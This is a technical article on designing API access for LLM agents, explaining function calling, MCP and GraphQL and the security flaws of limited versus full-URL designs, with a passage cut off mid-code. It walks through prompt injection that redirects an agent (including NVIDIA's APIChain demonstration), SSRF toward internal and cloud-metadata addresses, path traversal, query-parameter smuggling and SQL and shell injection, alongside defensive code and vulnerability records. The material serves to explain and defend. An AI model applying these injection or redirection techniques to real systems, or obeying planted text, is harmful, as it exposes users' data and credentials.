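# How much of an API call should a language model write? Limited and extensive API access for LLM agents

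## What is in an API call, and which parts can a model write?

A large language model (LLM) takes in text and produces text. An LLM agent is a program that connects an LLM to other software so that the model's output has effects outside the conversation, such as sending an email, issuing a refund or changing a database record. Most of these actions go through an application programming interface (API), the set of requests that one program accepts from others. In ordinary software, a programmer writes the request once and the program fills in the values. The designer of an agent can let the model write a single value, most of the request or all of it.

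Limited and extensive access are the two ends of this range. Under limited access, the developer fixes the request in advance and the model supplies only some of its values. Under extensive access, the model writes the structure of the request, whether that is a URL (web address), an operation in the query language GraphQL, or code that sends requests.

Take a customer-service agent for an online shop. A customer asks where a parcel is, and the agent has to look up the order. The shop's API has an endpoint for this, an endpoint being one address and method at which an API performs one operation:

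```
GET https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/{order_id}
```

### The parts of a request

For order 1042, the request that travels over the network might look like this:

```
GET /v1/orders/1042?fields=status,carrier HTTP/1.1
Host: api.shop.example
Accept: application/json
Authorization: Bearer ACCESS_TOKEN
```

GET is the method. By convention, GET only reads, POST creates or submits something, PUT and PATCH edit, and DELETE removes. The host, api.shop.example, identifies the server. The path, /v1/orders/1042, identifies the record, and the query string after the question mark adjusts the request, here by limiting the reply to two fields. The remaining lines are headers, which carry information about the request, such as the format the caller wants back. A GET request normally has no body, but if the shop accepts refunds by POST at /v1/orders/1042/refunds, the body of that request could hold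 an amount and a reason.

Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues (2025), in *Benchmarking LLMs in Web API Integration Tasks*, explain why a web API request is harder to write than a call to a function in the same program. The request identifies an operation by a method and a long URL, while a local call uses just a name. The request's values go in several separate places, and the documentation is kept elsewhere, often in a long and complicated format.

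The last header carries the credential, a secret that identifies the caller to the API and that the model doesn't need to see. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) examines where the credential is stored while the agent's request is sent, and how much of it an attacker who has taken over the agent's instructions could obtain. The paper proposes a vault, in which trusted code keeps the credential and attaches it outside the model. This protects the credential from theft but doesn't limit what it gives access to. In many designs, the credential belongs to the shop's own software and gives access to every order in the database, so a model that never sees it can still cause the software to request the wrong order.

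### How function calling works

The host code, the ordinary program around the model, checks what the model wrote and sends the request to the shop, so the model never contacts the shop directly. The usual arrangement is called function calling or tool calling, and OpenAI's developer guide, *Function calling*, divides it into five steps.

The host code begins by sending the model the conversation together with a list of tools. A tool is an operation that host code offers to the model, with a name, a description and a list of parameters (named slots that take a value). The machine-readable statement of which parameters a tool takes, and of what type, is the tool schema. For the order lookup the whole definition could be:

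```
{
  "type": "function",
  "name": "get_order",
  "description": "Look up one order by its number.",
  "parameters": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "order_id": { "type": "string" } },
    "required": ["order_id"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  },
  "strict": true
}
```

It contains neither the shop's address nor the token. In the second step the model returns only text, consisting of a tool name and values (here `get_order` with an `order_id` of "1042"). In the third step the host code reads the values, puts 1042 into the URL, adds the token, sends the GET request and receives the order. It then passes the result back to the model with an identifier that links it to the call. Finally the model either writes an answer for the customer or returns another tool call, in which case the loop repeats.

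Any checking happens in the third step. In Aalto University's course text *Tools, Agents, and Workflow Automation*, the application inspects and validates the model's call before executing it. The sample code in OpenAI's guide matches the tool's name, then passes the model's value to the function without checking it. That is acceptable for the guide's example, a horoscope lookup, but would not be for refunds. The "strict" setting in the definition above makes the model's output conform reliably to the schema, so the host code receives one string called `order_id` and nothing else. The setting controls only the output's form, so "1024" fits the schema as well as "1042" does.

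### OpenAPI, MCP and GraphQL

Developers rarely write every tool by hand. They can generate tools from an OpenAPI document, which is a machine-readable description of a web API's endpoints and their parameters. Maninger and colleagues call OpenAPI the most widely used specification standard for web APIs. An OpenAPI document can serve either kind of design. Cloudflare's *API reference* describes a function that turns the document into tool schemas automatically. *RestGPT* (2023), an early system for connecting models to web APIs, gave the document to the models instead. One module read the endpoint descriptions and selected an API, and another read the detailed documentation and wrote the parameters and the request body.

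The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common way for servers to offer tools to agents. Nordic APIs' *Exploring the Role of APIs in Agentic AI* describes it as Anthropic's proposal for a universal standard, made up of MCP servers and MCP clients. MCP standardizes how a tool reaches the agent, but the tool's author decides how much of the request to fix in advance. An MCP server for the shop could offer `get_order`, or a tool that fetches any address on the internet.

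GraphQL is a different style of API. The caller writes an operation, which is a query (read) or a mutation (write) that names the fields wanted:

```
query { order(id: "1042") { status carrier } }
```

The shop's first API had a separate address for each kind of record. A GraphQL API commonly has one address for everything, and the text of the operation determines what comes back.

### A scale from a fixed call to a free one

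The order lookup can sit at any of five steps, which differ in how much the model writes.

1. The model triggers a fixed call. The tool is `get_this_order()` and has no parameters, because the customer opened the chat from an order page and the host code already has the number. OpenAI's guide recommends this wherever it is possible, with the example of a `submit_refund()` tool that leaves the order number to code. All that remains for the model is whether to call the tool, and when.
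2. The model picks a value from a list. The host code looks up the customer's own orders and offers 1042, 1057 and 1063 as the only permitted values of `order_id`.
3. The model fills typed parameters. This is the `get_order` tool above. In the agent configuration that Docker documents, the developer writes the method, the headers and an address with marked gaps, and the model supplies values for the gaps. The step is a broad one, since an order number and a paragraph of free text can both have the type "string".
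4. The model writes the path and query on a fixed host. The tool is `shop_get(path)`. The model may write /v1/orders/1042 or /v1/customers/77, and the host code puts https://api.shop.example in front and adds the token. The model now chooses the endpoint, including endpoints that the developer did not have in mind.
5. The model writes the whole URL, the method and the body. The tool is `http_request(method, url, body)`. It can produce the same order lookup, a DELETE, or a request to another server altogether, which opens the way to server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attack that makes a server send a request to a destination of the attacker's choosing.

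The first three steps are limited access and the last two are extensive access. Maninger and colleagues tested nearly the same contrast in their benchmark. In one setup, the model wrote the entire call. In the other, it received the method and URL and wrote only the arguments, and almost every measure of correctness was better.

Model-written GraphQL operations belong at the extensive end of the scale, even if the host, path and method are constant and the tool schema has only a single string parameter called `query`. That string determines which records and fields the API returns and whether the call reads or writes, so counting parameters is a poor way to place a tool on the scale. The agent can even work out the operation as it goes. In a recap of its AI working group, GraphQL (2026) describes an agent that starts from the schema's top-level fields and builds a valid operation from there.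 If the developer has written and approved the operation beforehand and only the variables change, the tool belongs at the third step.

Code is the other extensive form. OpenAI's guide includes custom tools that accept arbitrary text instead of typed values, such as one that executes Python. A short program can loop over a thousand order numbers, so one model output may lead to a thousand requests. A system can let the model write code and still restrict where that code sends requests. In *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026), an agent called Baya searches for relevant endpoints and then writes a restricted Python script. The script can compute locally, but it reaches the website only through trusted APIs and has no unrestricted network access.

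A designer would go beyond the third step mostly to cover more of an API. The Slack API in Maninger and colleagues' dataset has 174 endpoints, while OpenAI's soft suggestion is to offer a model fewer than 20 functions at the start of a turn. One narrow tool per endpoint would quickly exceed that number. Searching for tools on demand eases the problem, as OpenAI notes. A tool that lets the model write the path removes the problem, but it also gives the model access to everything else the path can reach.

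The origin of the labels "limited" and "extensive" API access is unclear. Both appear in summaries of the *Securing Agentic Applications Guide 1.0* (2025) from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a community that publishes security guidance. According to *Agentic Applications Under Attack*, a summary by the consultancy Elevate, the guide's list of agent components includes "Limited API Access", in which endpoints are predefined and the model generates parameters, and "Extensive API Access", in which the agent constructs entire calls. SecurityCareers.help's *Securing the Autonomous Frontier* also attributes the second label to the guide. Neither summary credits OWASP with coining the labels, which work better as descriptions than as a standard.

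### More freedom is not always more harm

The scale orders designs by what the model writes, not by how much damage a bad request can do. The tool `delete_customer(customer_id)` is at the third step, and one wrong number can destroy an account. An agent that may read any of a fixed set of public web pages, without credentials or access to private data, has more choice but can do far less damage.

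The difference is in authority, which designers often grant more broadly than a task needs. *AC4A* (2026), a proposal for access control in agents, describes current systems as all-or-nothing. A user who wants the agent to create one calendar event must grant it the entire calendar API, including the power to change existing events. OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* advises developers to limit both what the model writes, by avoiding open-ended extensions such as one that fetches a URL, and what the tool can do, by leaving deleting and sending out of a tool that only has to summarise mail. The shop's designer has to set these two limits separately for every tool.

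### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Prompt injection is text from an untrusted source that a model reads and treats as an instruction. The developer's rules, the customer's question and the shop API's last reply all reach the model as text, and the model cannot reliably tell which of them it should take instructions from. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) explains the name by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which text that a user typed as data runs as part of a database command. Some researchers separate direct injection, where the user is the attacker, from indirect injection, where the text arrives in a document or a tool's reply, but this paper uses one term for both.

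In the shop, the text could be in a gift message. Somebody writes the message when placing an order, and when the agent fetches that order days later, the message enters the model's context along with the delivery status. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, which manipulates people with plausible stories, so the message need not look like a command. In one example from 2025, an email posing as a routine follow-up on staff changes succeeded in 50% of tests with a particular user request.

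Even a design from the first step of the scale lets such text reach the model, because function calling returns the API's reply to it. An ordinary `get_order` tool, for example, limits what the model can choose but still returns the result. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose an "action-selector" pattern that prevents this. The model picks from predefined actions or fills placeholders in a template, and the results never go back to it.

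The writer of the gift message cannot read other people's orders, but the agent can, because the host code attaches the shop's token to its requests. The old computer security term for a program in this position is "confused deputy", meaning a program that is induced to use its authority for someone who lacks it. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists confused-deputy behaviour among the risks of tool-using models and points out that agents hold delegated authority, so a harmful output may become a transaction or a database update. *GreyZone* (2026), a paper on threats to agent applications, describes the same mechanism without the name and adds that the attack's success depends on both how the agent interprets the planted text and which controls its environment enforces. A developer can set those controls in code. When the agent asks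 for a stranger's order, the request has the correct format and a valid token, but object-level authorization can still stop it by checking whether this user may act on this particular record.

Bad requests can also arise without an attacker. If a customer types 1042 and the model writes 1024, the API returns a stranger's address. *Mapping LLM Security Landscapes* (2024) describes a file summariser whose plugin can also modify and delete files. If a user complains about a mistake in the summary, the model may respond by altering the file. Akamai, a security vendor, warns about both attacks and model errors when it refers to a "manipulated or unreliable model" with access to sensitive data.

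The two origins call for partly different defences. A filter that searches incoming text for planted instructions won't catch two swapped digits. Host code that checks whether order 1024 belongs to this customer will stop the request if it doesn't, whatever the cause. Attacks are also harder to predict by testing. A developer can estimate the rate of ordinary errors from a sample of ordinary conversations, but that sample gives little idea of how the agent will fare against someone who keeps rewording a gift message until the attack works.

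## If the model fills in only the parameters, what can still go wrong?

Under limited access, a value from the model can contain characters that change the request's structure, so that the model writes more of the request than the developer intended. A value can also be correctly formed but refer to a record that the user has no right to see.

### How the host code builds the request

The developer starts with a URL template, an address with named gaps:

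```
https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/{order_id}?fields={fields}
```

The earlier `get_order` schema accepted any string as an order number. A tighter one, covering both gaps, looks like this:

```
"order_id": { "type": "string", "pattern": "^[0-9]{4,8}$" },
"fields":   { "type": "string", "enum": ["status", "status,carrier"] }
```

The pattern allows four to eight digits, and the enumeration (`enum`) allows two exact strings. The schema can also set a minimum and a maximum for a number, such as a refund amount. Developers often put such limits in the parameter's description instead, where they guide the model but are not enforced. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (Shi, Fu and colleagues, 2026) collected the definitions of 1,856 tools on 100 MCP servers. About 77% of the tools had parameter descriptions with some operational constraint,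 such as a required format, and under 2% had any security restriction.

The model's provider can enforce a schema while the model writes, a technique called constrained decoding. A language model produces text one token (a word fragment or character) at a time, and before each step it assigns a probability to every token it could write next. The decoder works out which tokens could still lead to valid output, sets the probability of all the others to zero and rescales the rest. If $A$ is the set of permitted tokens and $p(t)$ is the model's probability for token $t$, the new probability of a permitted token is

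$$p'(t) = \frac{p(t)}{\sum_{u \in A} p(u)}$$

Suppose the model has written 104 and assigns a 60% probability to the next character being the digit 2, 10% to the digit 5 and 30% to a slash. The pattern rules out the slash, so the probability of the 2 rises to 0.6/0.7, or about 86%, and that of the 5 to about 14%.

Rescaling can turn an invalid call into one that is valid but wrong. If the schema lists orders 1042, 1057 and 1063 and the customer asks about a different order, a model that has already begun the call can only pick one of the three. Adding a value such as "none" lets it avoid choosing a wrong order.

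The host code should still validate every value against the schema, because providers' decoders differ in which schema rules they support. Decoders also can't constrain values that someone sends straight to the tool without using the model. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) notes that attackers can exploit the flaws it identifies in MCP server code with no LLM involved.

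Some values are better left to ordinary code. In a Cohere example, users type long product codes, and the agent must copy each one exactly and put it under the right parameter name. A deterministic function finds the codes by their patterns and labels them, but the model still copies them into the final request. A stricter version would have the host code insert them, so the model would handle only the values that require interpreting language, such as mapping "tennis products" to the category SPORT.

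### One tool for every endpoint

A generator that works from an OpenAPI document makes one tool from each operation. The operation's name and summary become the tool's name and description, its parameters become the tool schema, and the host code keeps the method and the URL template. Cloudflare's generator also lets the developer select endpoints with match patterns and set authentication headers in the configuration.

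The model can only fill in the parameters of each generated call, but the set of calls can cover every operation in the API document. If the shop's document describes `DELETE /v1/customers/{customer_id}` alongside the order lookup, a generator that converts everything gives a delivery-tracking agent the power to delete accounts. This can make the generated set more dangerous than `shop_get(path)`, which can only read data. The remedy is to choose the operations before generating any calls, starting from an empty list and adding the ones the agent needs.

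Some developers convert entire web APIs to MCP. In *Hunt Them All*, a survey of open-source MCP servers for the security vendor Trend Micro, Oliveira and Fiser found one source file with 14,764 blocks of defensive code, which they attribute to such a conversion.

The OpenAPI document is also an input, and developers often fetch it from a third party. Orval, a code generator that can produce MCP code from these documents, used to copy an operation's summary into the generated program without escaping it. As He and colleagues describe, a malicious summary could run code on the developer's machine during generation, before any agent existed. Version 7.18.0 fixed this. The model also reads the summary as the tool's description, so the summary can carry a prompt injection too.

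### A path separator in the order number

If the schema allows any string and the host code pastes the value into the template, the value can change which endpoint is called. For example, `1042/refunds` gives the path `/v1/orders/1042/refunds`. A segment of two dots means "one level up", so a longer value can reach paths outside `/v1/orders`. A question mark ends the path, so anything the template had after the parameter is dropped from it.

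FastMCP, a Python library for building MCP servers, had this flaw in its OpenAPI generator until version 3.2.0. According to the US National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-32871 Detail*, the library put values into the template unencoded and then called a standard function that resolves the two-dot segments. It sent the request with the authorization headers configured on the server. GitHub rated the flaw 10.0, the highest severity score. OSV's advisory, *PYSEC-2026-338* (2026), demonstrates how the user ID in a profile lookup can lead to an administrative endpoint that isn't in the OpenAPI document. Developers who used the generator had built limited designs, but the missing encoding gave callers much of the access they would have had with a tool that accepts any path on the server.

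Percent-encoding fixes this by replacing each special character with a percent sign and a two-digit code. A slash becomes `%2F` and a question mark becomes `%3F`, so the server reads both as part of the value. OSV recommends encoding every path value, with no character exempted.

Encoding alone leaves a small gap. The advisory lists the dot among the characters its fix will encode, but the Python function the fix uses leaves dots unchanged because the URL standard treats them as ordinary characters. A value consisting only of two dots is therefore unchanged and still means "one level up". Host code should reject such a value, which the digits-only pattern already does.

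It also helps if the shop resolves the URL first and then checks that it still points to one order under /v1/orders/. Anthropic's official MCP server for Git, the version-control program, had a related flaw in its handling of file paths. The server was supposed to stay inside one repository, but it didn't properly check the path it received against that limit, so an attacker could steer it into a neighbouring repository. He et al. conclude that an access check has to use the same normalized path that the underlying tool will use.

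### An ampersand in a query value

An ampersand separates parameters in a query string. If the host code pastes `status&expand=customer` into the `fields` gap, the shop receives two parameters. If its API has an `expand` option, the reply will include the customer's record as well as the delivery status.

The result can be worse when the host code has put its own restriction in the query string. For example, a product or order search might end in `&customer=77` to limit it to one person's records. If the search term adds a second `customer` parameter, the server receives two values for the same name, and servers differ in which one they use. A milder version can happen without an attacker, as when a customer searches for "salt & pepper mill" and gets results for "salt".

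*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists "URL Parameter Injection" for tools that construct URLs from untrusted input. To prevent it, the host code should pass names and values separately to the HTTP library instead of joining them as text. The library then writes the ampersand as `%26`. Each value should be encoded only once, because encoding it twice sends the shop a literal "%26" instead of an ampersand. Similarly, a JSON library should handle the quoting in a request body. Predefined GraphQL operations keep values in variables for the same reason.

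### A value that reaches SQL or a shell

Percent-encoding protects a value only until the API decodes it. If the code behind the API then pastes the value into an SQL statement, a quotation mark in the value can end the string early, and the database will run the rest as a command. *MCPGuard* (2025) describes MCP servers that concatenate LLM-generated parameters into SQL queries, or into functions that execute code or shell commands.

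For SQL the fix is a parameterized query, in which the database receives the statement and the value separately and never parses the value as SQL:

```
SELECT status, carrier FROM orders WHERE id = ?
```

The safest alternative to running a command-line program is a library function that does the same job. If there isn't one, the code can start the program directly with a list of arguments, without using a shell. Even then, the program may treat a value that begins with a hyphen as an option. Anthropic's Git server passed tool arguments to the Git command line unsanitized until version 2025.12.17, and He and colleagues explain how somebody who influenced those arguments through prompt injection could add an option and run commands with the server's privileges. Code that wraps a program can reject values that start with a hyphen. Many programs also accept a marker that stops them from treating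 anything after it as an option.

Requiring an order number to match a digits-only pattern would prevent the path, ampersand, SQL and shell problems. A customer's reason for a refund can't be limited this way because it has to allow apostrophes and ampersands. Every stage needs to handle free text correctly, and the agent's developer may not control the code at the last stage.

Shi and colleagues propose SpellSmith, a defence for servers that nobody can readily change. It rewrites tool descriptions to include specific warnings and asks the model to reconsider each call before sending it. In tests on GPT-4o, a 2024 model, with 792 malicious prompts, attacks succeeded in 56.61% of trials with no defence, 2.19% with reconsideration alone and 0.04% with both measures. Without reconsideration, attacks succeeded less often when descriptions named the wrong vulnerability (9.89%) than when they gave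 a correct but generic warning (21.63%), so some of the benefit probably comes from making the model cautious in general.

The paper proposes warning the model as an alternative to repairing code. Its concern about repairs is reasonable, because fixes in its sample changed 204 lines on average, and 4 of 41 left the flaw exploitable. But a warning only makes an exploit less likely, and it doesn't protect against callers who bypass the model. A parameterized query prevents injection for every value from every caller.

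### A valid number for somebody else's order

The model may fill in an order number, such as 1024, that belongs to another customer. The number matches the pattern, needs no encoding and fits safely into a parameterized query, so none of the fixes above stops the request.

A better schema would not stop it either. A schema describes the form that all order numbers share, not which order belongs to which user, and that information changes whenever somebody places an order. Long random identifiers make guessing harder, but they turn up in emails, links and screenshots.

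Object-level authorization does work, provided that the host code or the shop's API applies it on every request. The simplest place for it is the query itself:

```
SELECT status, carrier FROM orders WHERE id = ? AND customer_id = ?
```

The second value comes from the login session. If the query finds nothing, the agent reports "order not found", whether the order doesn't exist or belongs to another customer. Different messages for the two cases would let anyone learn which order numbers are in use.

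Listing the customer's own orders as the only permitted values may look like a schema that solves the problem. In that design the host code has already looked up who owns what, and the schema only carries the result. The list can go out of date during a long conversation, and a caller who bypasses the decoder can send any number at all, so the check at the time of the request remains necessary. (A choice from a short list can also leak information, if an attacker can observe which request follows.)

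The best place for the check depends on the credential. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* recommends per-user OAuth, a standard way for a user to delegate limited access to a program, over shared administrator tokens. With a token tied to the customer, the shop's API can refuse a request for order 1024 by itself. With a shared token, the API can't distinguish one customer's requests from another's, so the host code has to do the checking. The paper recommends that, with either kind of token, fixed code outside the model check the user's entitlement, along with the host, method, path and volume of requests. Actions need their own rules, because a customer who may view an order isn't necessarily due a refund on it.

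A search for injection flaws won't reveal that this check is missing. *MCP-in-SoS* (2026), a framework for assessing MCP servers, classifies missing authorization separately from SQL and command injection. Prompt injection can exploit missing authorization without either of those flaws, because planted text can steer the model to valid values. OSV's *CVE-2026-13341* (2026) reports that before version 1.0.0 of Kong Konnect's MCP server, a prompt injection in untrusted analytics data could lead to unintended API requests.

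### What the host code should fill in itself

The ownership check offers no protection if the model can set the user's identity. Suppose `get_order` had a `customer_id` parameter as well as the order number. The model would normally fill in the right ID, but a planted message could cause it to fill in the ID of another customer, whose order it was requesting, and the check would pass. The user's identity has to come from the login session and should not appear in the tool schema.

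The same goes for the tenant, meaning the organization whose data a request concerns when several share one system. If the software behind our shop also serves a hundred other shops, a wrong tenant exposes another company's customers. Credentials complete the list. In outline, the whole tool is:

```
def get_order(session, args):
    order_id = args["order_id"]
    if not re.fullmatch(r"[0-9]{4,8}", order_id):
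        return {"error": "invalid order number"}
    if not owns_order(session.tenant_id, session.customer_id, order_id):
        return {"error": "order not found"}
    return http_get(
        "https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/" + quote(order_id, safe=""),
        params={"fields": "status,carrier"},
        headers={"Authorization": "Bearer " + vault.token("shop")},
        follow_redirects=False)
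```

The model supplies `order_id`, and the session supplies everything else the ownership check needs. The code reads only that argument from the model's output. A common shortcut is to merge all of the output into the request, but if the merge order is wrong, a made-up `customer_id` can overwrite the real one. The last line stops the HTTP library from following a redirect, which might send the token to another server.

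### Two experiments on keeping credentials away from the agent

Researchers at Corvic AI, which sells a credential vault, tested part of this arrangement on 27 September 2026 and reported the results in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*. In their product, code the agent runs refers to a connector, a stored record for one outside service, and the vault adds the credential to requests to that service's declared address.

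The researchers ran two experiments inside the product's sandbox, an isolated environment that restricts what code can reach. Each used one connector and a fixed list of probes, with pass criteria set beforehand. In one experiment, the connector led to FRED, a source of economic data. The probes searched the environment variables and 12 common file locations for secrets, and tried the internal addresses from which cloud machines can obtain credentials. They also called three echo services, which return whatever headers they receive, to check whether the vault would attach the credential to a request for the wrong site. The other experiment used a GitHub connector and mainly tested whether a legitimate request would work.

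All 16 scored probes passed. GitHub accepted the request and returned the account's identity, although the code that made the request held no credential. The echo services received no credential, and an unrelated OpenAI API rejected its request as unauthenticated. The other results would mean little without the GitHub success, because a sandbox with no network connection would also leak nothing.

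The legitimate request to FRED failed because the vault put the key in a header, while FRED expects it in the query string. Nothing leaked, and the researchers scored the failure separately as a configuration fault.

Sixteen hand-picked probes can't establish a failure rate, and these came from the vendor. The researchers didn't test redirects, changes to the address behind a hostname, or a compromised destination. They ran fixed scripts instead of attacking a live model, and they say a standard prompt-injection benchmark would be the most valuable next step. In their rough scoring, on a scale up to 25, the vault lowers the threat score for code finding a credential from 20 to 4, but the score for a connector with too many privileges only from 20 to 15.

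### How common are these flaws in MCP servers?

Several groups have counted vulnerabilities in MCP software. Two studies, by Shi and colleagues and by He and colleagues, started from public vulnerability records. Oliveira and Fiser used AI agents to search source code and checked a sample of the results by hand. In *Exposed by Design*, Padilla (2026) tested servers that were live on the internet in July 2026.

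| Study | Sample | Injection and path flaws | Access control |
|---|---|---|---|
| He and colleagues | 24 published vulnerabilities in MCP servers, clients and development kits | 7 command injection, 5 path traversal, 4 remote code execution | 4 with inadequate access control |
| Shi and colleagues | 53 vulnerabilities on 45 servers | 27 command injection, 9 path traversal, 2 code injection, 2 SQL injection | 6 unauthorized access |
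| Oliveira and Fiser | 93 confirmed flaws, from 2,287 candidates | 26% SQL injection, 22.5% remote code execution, 19% path traversal | 7.5% authentication bypass |
| Padilla | 414 live servers | 68 reportable flaws of all kinds, including SQL injection and path traversal | 91.8% of servers without OAuth |

The counts of published vulnerabilities point to the same main cause. He and colleagues attribute 18 of their 24 cases to poor input validation, and in Shi and colleagues' sample, 40 of 53 flaws take effect when the agent calls a tool. But the samples overlap, and sorting the flaws involves considerable judgement. Both groups searched for "MCP" in records up to February 2026 and got almost the same number of hits (119 and 116), but one kept 11 flaws in servers and the other kept 35. We also can't use such counts to estimate how many servers are vulnerable, because they leave out every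 server that nobody has examined.

Oliveira and Fiser estimate that there are 600 to 1,650 vulnerabilities across about 19,000 repositories. Their central figure of 770 looks wrong. They found that 4.1% of the candidate flaws were genuine and multiplied this by the number of repositories, but the candidates came from a pool of just over 15,000. Multiplying by the size of the pool gives a little over 600. The true number could still be higher, because their agent discarded 1,849 candidates that no person reviewed.

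Padilla's live tests come closest to showing what an attacker would find, but outsiders can't check most of the 68 flaws, because 49 were still under embargo when the paper appeared. A server without OAuth may use another form of authentication or serve only public data, so the 91.8% isn't the share of servers that are insecure.

Missing object-level authorization hardly shows up in these numbers because Oliveira and Fiser told their agent to ignore missing authentication and authorization. They reasoned that most MCP servers are known to have neither at the server level. So a server that returns order 1024 to anyone who requests it would have passed.

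## What goes wrong when the model writes the whole URL?

If the model writes the whole URL, it determines which server gets the request, whereas the host code does this when the model only fills in an order number. Anyone who can steer the model can then make the host code contact any address its machine can reach. A well-documented case is APIChain, a component of LangChain, an open-source library for building applications on language models.

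### How APIChain works

To use APIChain, a developer supplies a model, the API's documentation as plain text and any headers the API requires. In LangChain's source code, the host code gives the model the user's question and the documentation, and the model writes a URL. The host code fetches that URL with a GET request, adding the developer's headers. It then passes the response to the model, which writes the answer.

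To answer "Where is order 1042?", the model would write `https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/1042` and find the delivery status in the reply. The developer doesn't have to define any tools, and only has to update the documentation if the shop adds an endpoint. The documentation tells the model which addresses to use, but it is only text in the prompt, and the original version of APIChain fetched whatever address the model wrote.

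### How injected text changes the destination

A question to APIChain can contain instructions that conflict with the developer's. NVIDIA's *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection* describes how the company's AI Red Team, which looks for weaknesses in AI systems, exploited this. In its question, the team announced a new query and told the model to retrieve a different URL. The model wrote that URL, the host code fetched it, and the chain returned its contents. The team used text-davinci-003, an OpenAI model from 2022, and expected other models to need slightly different wording. The demonstration shows that the attack is possible, but the team gave no success rate.

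The attacker here was the user. A stranger's gift message couldn't redirect APIChain this way, because it would arrive in the API's response, after the model had written its only URL, though it could still distort the answer. In an agent that loops, the gift message is already in the context when the model writes its next URL, so the stranger can also influence where that request goes.

APIChain attaches the developer's headers to every request, whatever the address. Without a restriction on the destination, a request to the attacker's server gives the attacker the shop's token, even though the model has never seen it. The URL can also carry private data from the conversation. The request tool in LlamaIndex, another library for LLM applications, requires the developer to name the host for each set of headers, so the shop's token isn't sent to other servers.

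### What server-side request forgery can reach

An outsider usually can't connect to a company's internal network, but the host code often runs inside it. Some internal services have no login because their owners assume that only colleagues can reach them. Researchers at Unit 42, Palo Alto Networks' threat research group, demonstrated the danger with a LangChain component that reads a website's sitemap and fetches every page it lists. They put internal addresses in a sitemap, and the component retrieved a confidential page. They also used an internal API to run commands. The researchers wrote those URLs, but a model-written URL to the same service would have the same effect.

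Cloud servers have another sensitive address, 169.254.169.254. It leads to a metadata service that provides information about the machine and can issue temporary credentials for the company's cloud account. GitHub's *GHSA-GF3V-FWQG-4VH7* (2026), an advisory about a LangChain web crawler, lists these credentials among the things an attacker could obtain, along with access to private networks and to services on the crawler's own machine. The major cloud providers now require a special header on metadata requests, or let customers require one. A model that writes only the URL can't add that header, so the requirement blocks the simplest version of the attack.

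APIChain sends only GET requests, so the main risk is disclosure. With `http_request(method, url, body)`, the model chooses the HTTP method, so injected text could also lead it to change or delete data on an internal service.

If the URL leads to the attacker's page, the reply puts more of the attacker's text into the model's context. In APIChain that text can affect only the answer, for example by giving the customer a false phone number for refunds, but in a looping agent it can lead to further tool calls. A gift message may hold only a sentence or two, but that is enough to direct the agent to a page of any length, which the attacker can rewrite at any time.

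### CVE-2023-32786 and its repair

NVIDIA's team reported the flaw to LangChain on 20 April 2023, along with an SQL injection flaw in another chain. The URL flaw appeared in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities on 20 October as CVE-2023-32786, with a severity of 7.5 out of 10. The rating is based on a serious loss of confidentiality and no loss of integrity, although according to the description an attacker might also inject content into later tasks.

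Advisories differ on which versions are vulnerable. OSV's *CVE-2023-32786* (2023) lists versions through 0.0.155, and GitLab's *CVE-2023-32786* (2023) lists 0.0.156 as the fixed version. GitHub's *GHSA-6h8p-4hx9-w66c* (2023) and OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1508* (2026) instead list all versions before 0.0.329.

The later version number is much closer to correct. NVIDIA's team could still exploit APIChain in version 0.0.193, which rules out a fix in 0.0.156. Version 0.0.155 was probably the newest version tested when the record was drafted, and GitLab seems to have assumed that the next release fixed the flaw. GitHub's advisory, last modified on 2 November 2023, links to the code change that fixed it. GitLab's page still recommended "0.0.156 or above" in May 2026, so a developer who followed it could have installed a vulnerable version.

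According to Miggo, a security company, the code change added a setting called `limit_to_domains` to APIChain. The developer lists the permitted destinations, and the host code checks the scheme (such as `https`) and domain of each model-written URL against the list before fetching anything. Omitting the setting or supplying an empty list causes an error. A developer who wants no restriction has to set it to `None`, which LangChain advises against.

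This strict default broke LangChain's own tools for weather, films, podcasts and news, which used APIChain without a list of allowed domains. A contributor fixed them by adding a list for each in LangChain's *BUG Add limit_to_domains to APIChain based tools (#13367)*. The contributor first saw the error in version 0.0.328, so the default may have reached users one release earlier than the advisories indicate.

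### Where APIChain and LangChain's request tools stand now

APIChain stayed in LangChain's main package and received the repair there, although NVIDIA wrote that LangChain had removed the affected components from its latest version. LangChain deprecated APIChain in version 0.2.13 and later moved it to `langchain-classic`, a package for legacy code. On its *Chains* page, LangChain promises security maintenance for that package only until December 2026. The copy of the domain check in Supermodel's `_check_in_allowed_domain()` still works as it did before the move.

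APIChain also depends on `langchain-community`, a collection of third-party integrations, and users get an error without it, according to LangChain's *APIChain* reference page. LangChain (2026) announced in the package's version 0.4.2 notes that it is winding the package down.

LangChain's suggested replacement for APIChain gives the model general request tools, one each for GET, POST, PATCH, PUT and DELETE. The model writes the entire URL, and LangChain's example has no domain list. The tools won't start unless the developer sets `allow_dangerous_requests` to true. In the commit that introduced this flag, *Add dangerous parameter to requests tool (#18697)*, Yurtsev (2024) noted that the tools were already documented as dangerous and that it was unclear whether an opt-in was needed. The flag makes the developer acknowledge the risk but doesn't restrict any request once it is on.

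A developer who moves from the repaired APIChain to the suggested replacement therefore loses the domain check, unless they write their own. They also still depend on an ageing package, because the request tools are part of `langchain-community` too.

### How to check a URL

For an agent that should contact only the shop, the check could look like this in outline:

```
def check_url(url):
    u = urlsplit(url)
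    if (u.scheme, u.hostname, u.port or 443) != ("https", "api.shop.example", 443):
        raise Refused("wrong destination")
    addresses = resolve(u.hostname)
    if not addresses or not all(ip_address(a).is_global for a in addresses):
        raise Refused("not a public address")
    return addresses[0]

def fetch(url):
    for _ in range(4):
        address = check_url(url)
        reply = send_get(url, connect_to=address, follow_redirects=False)
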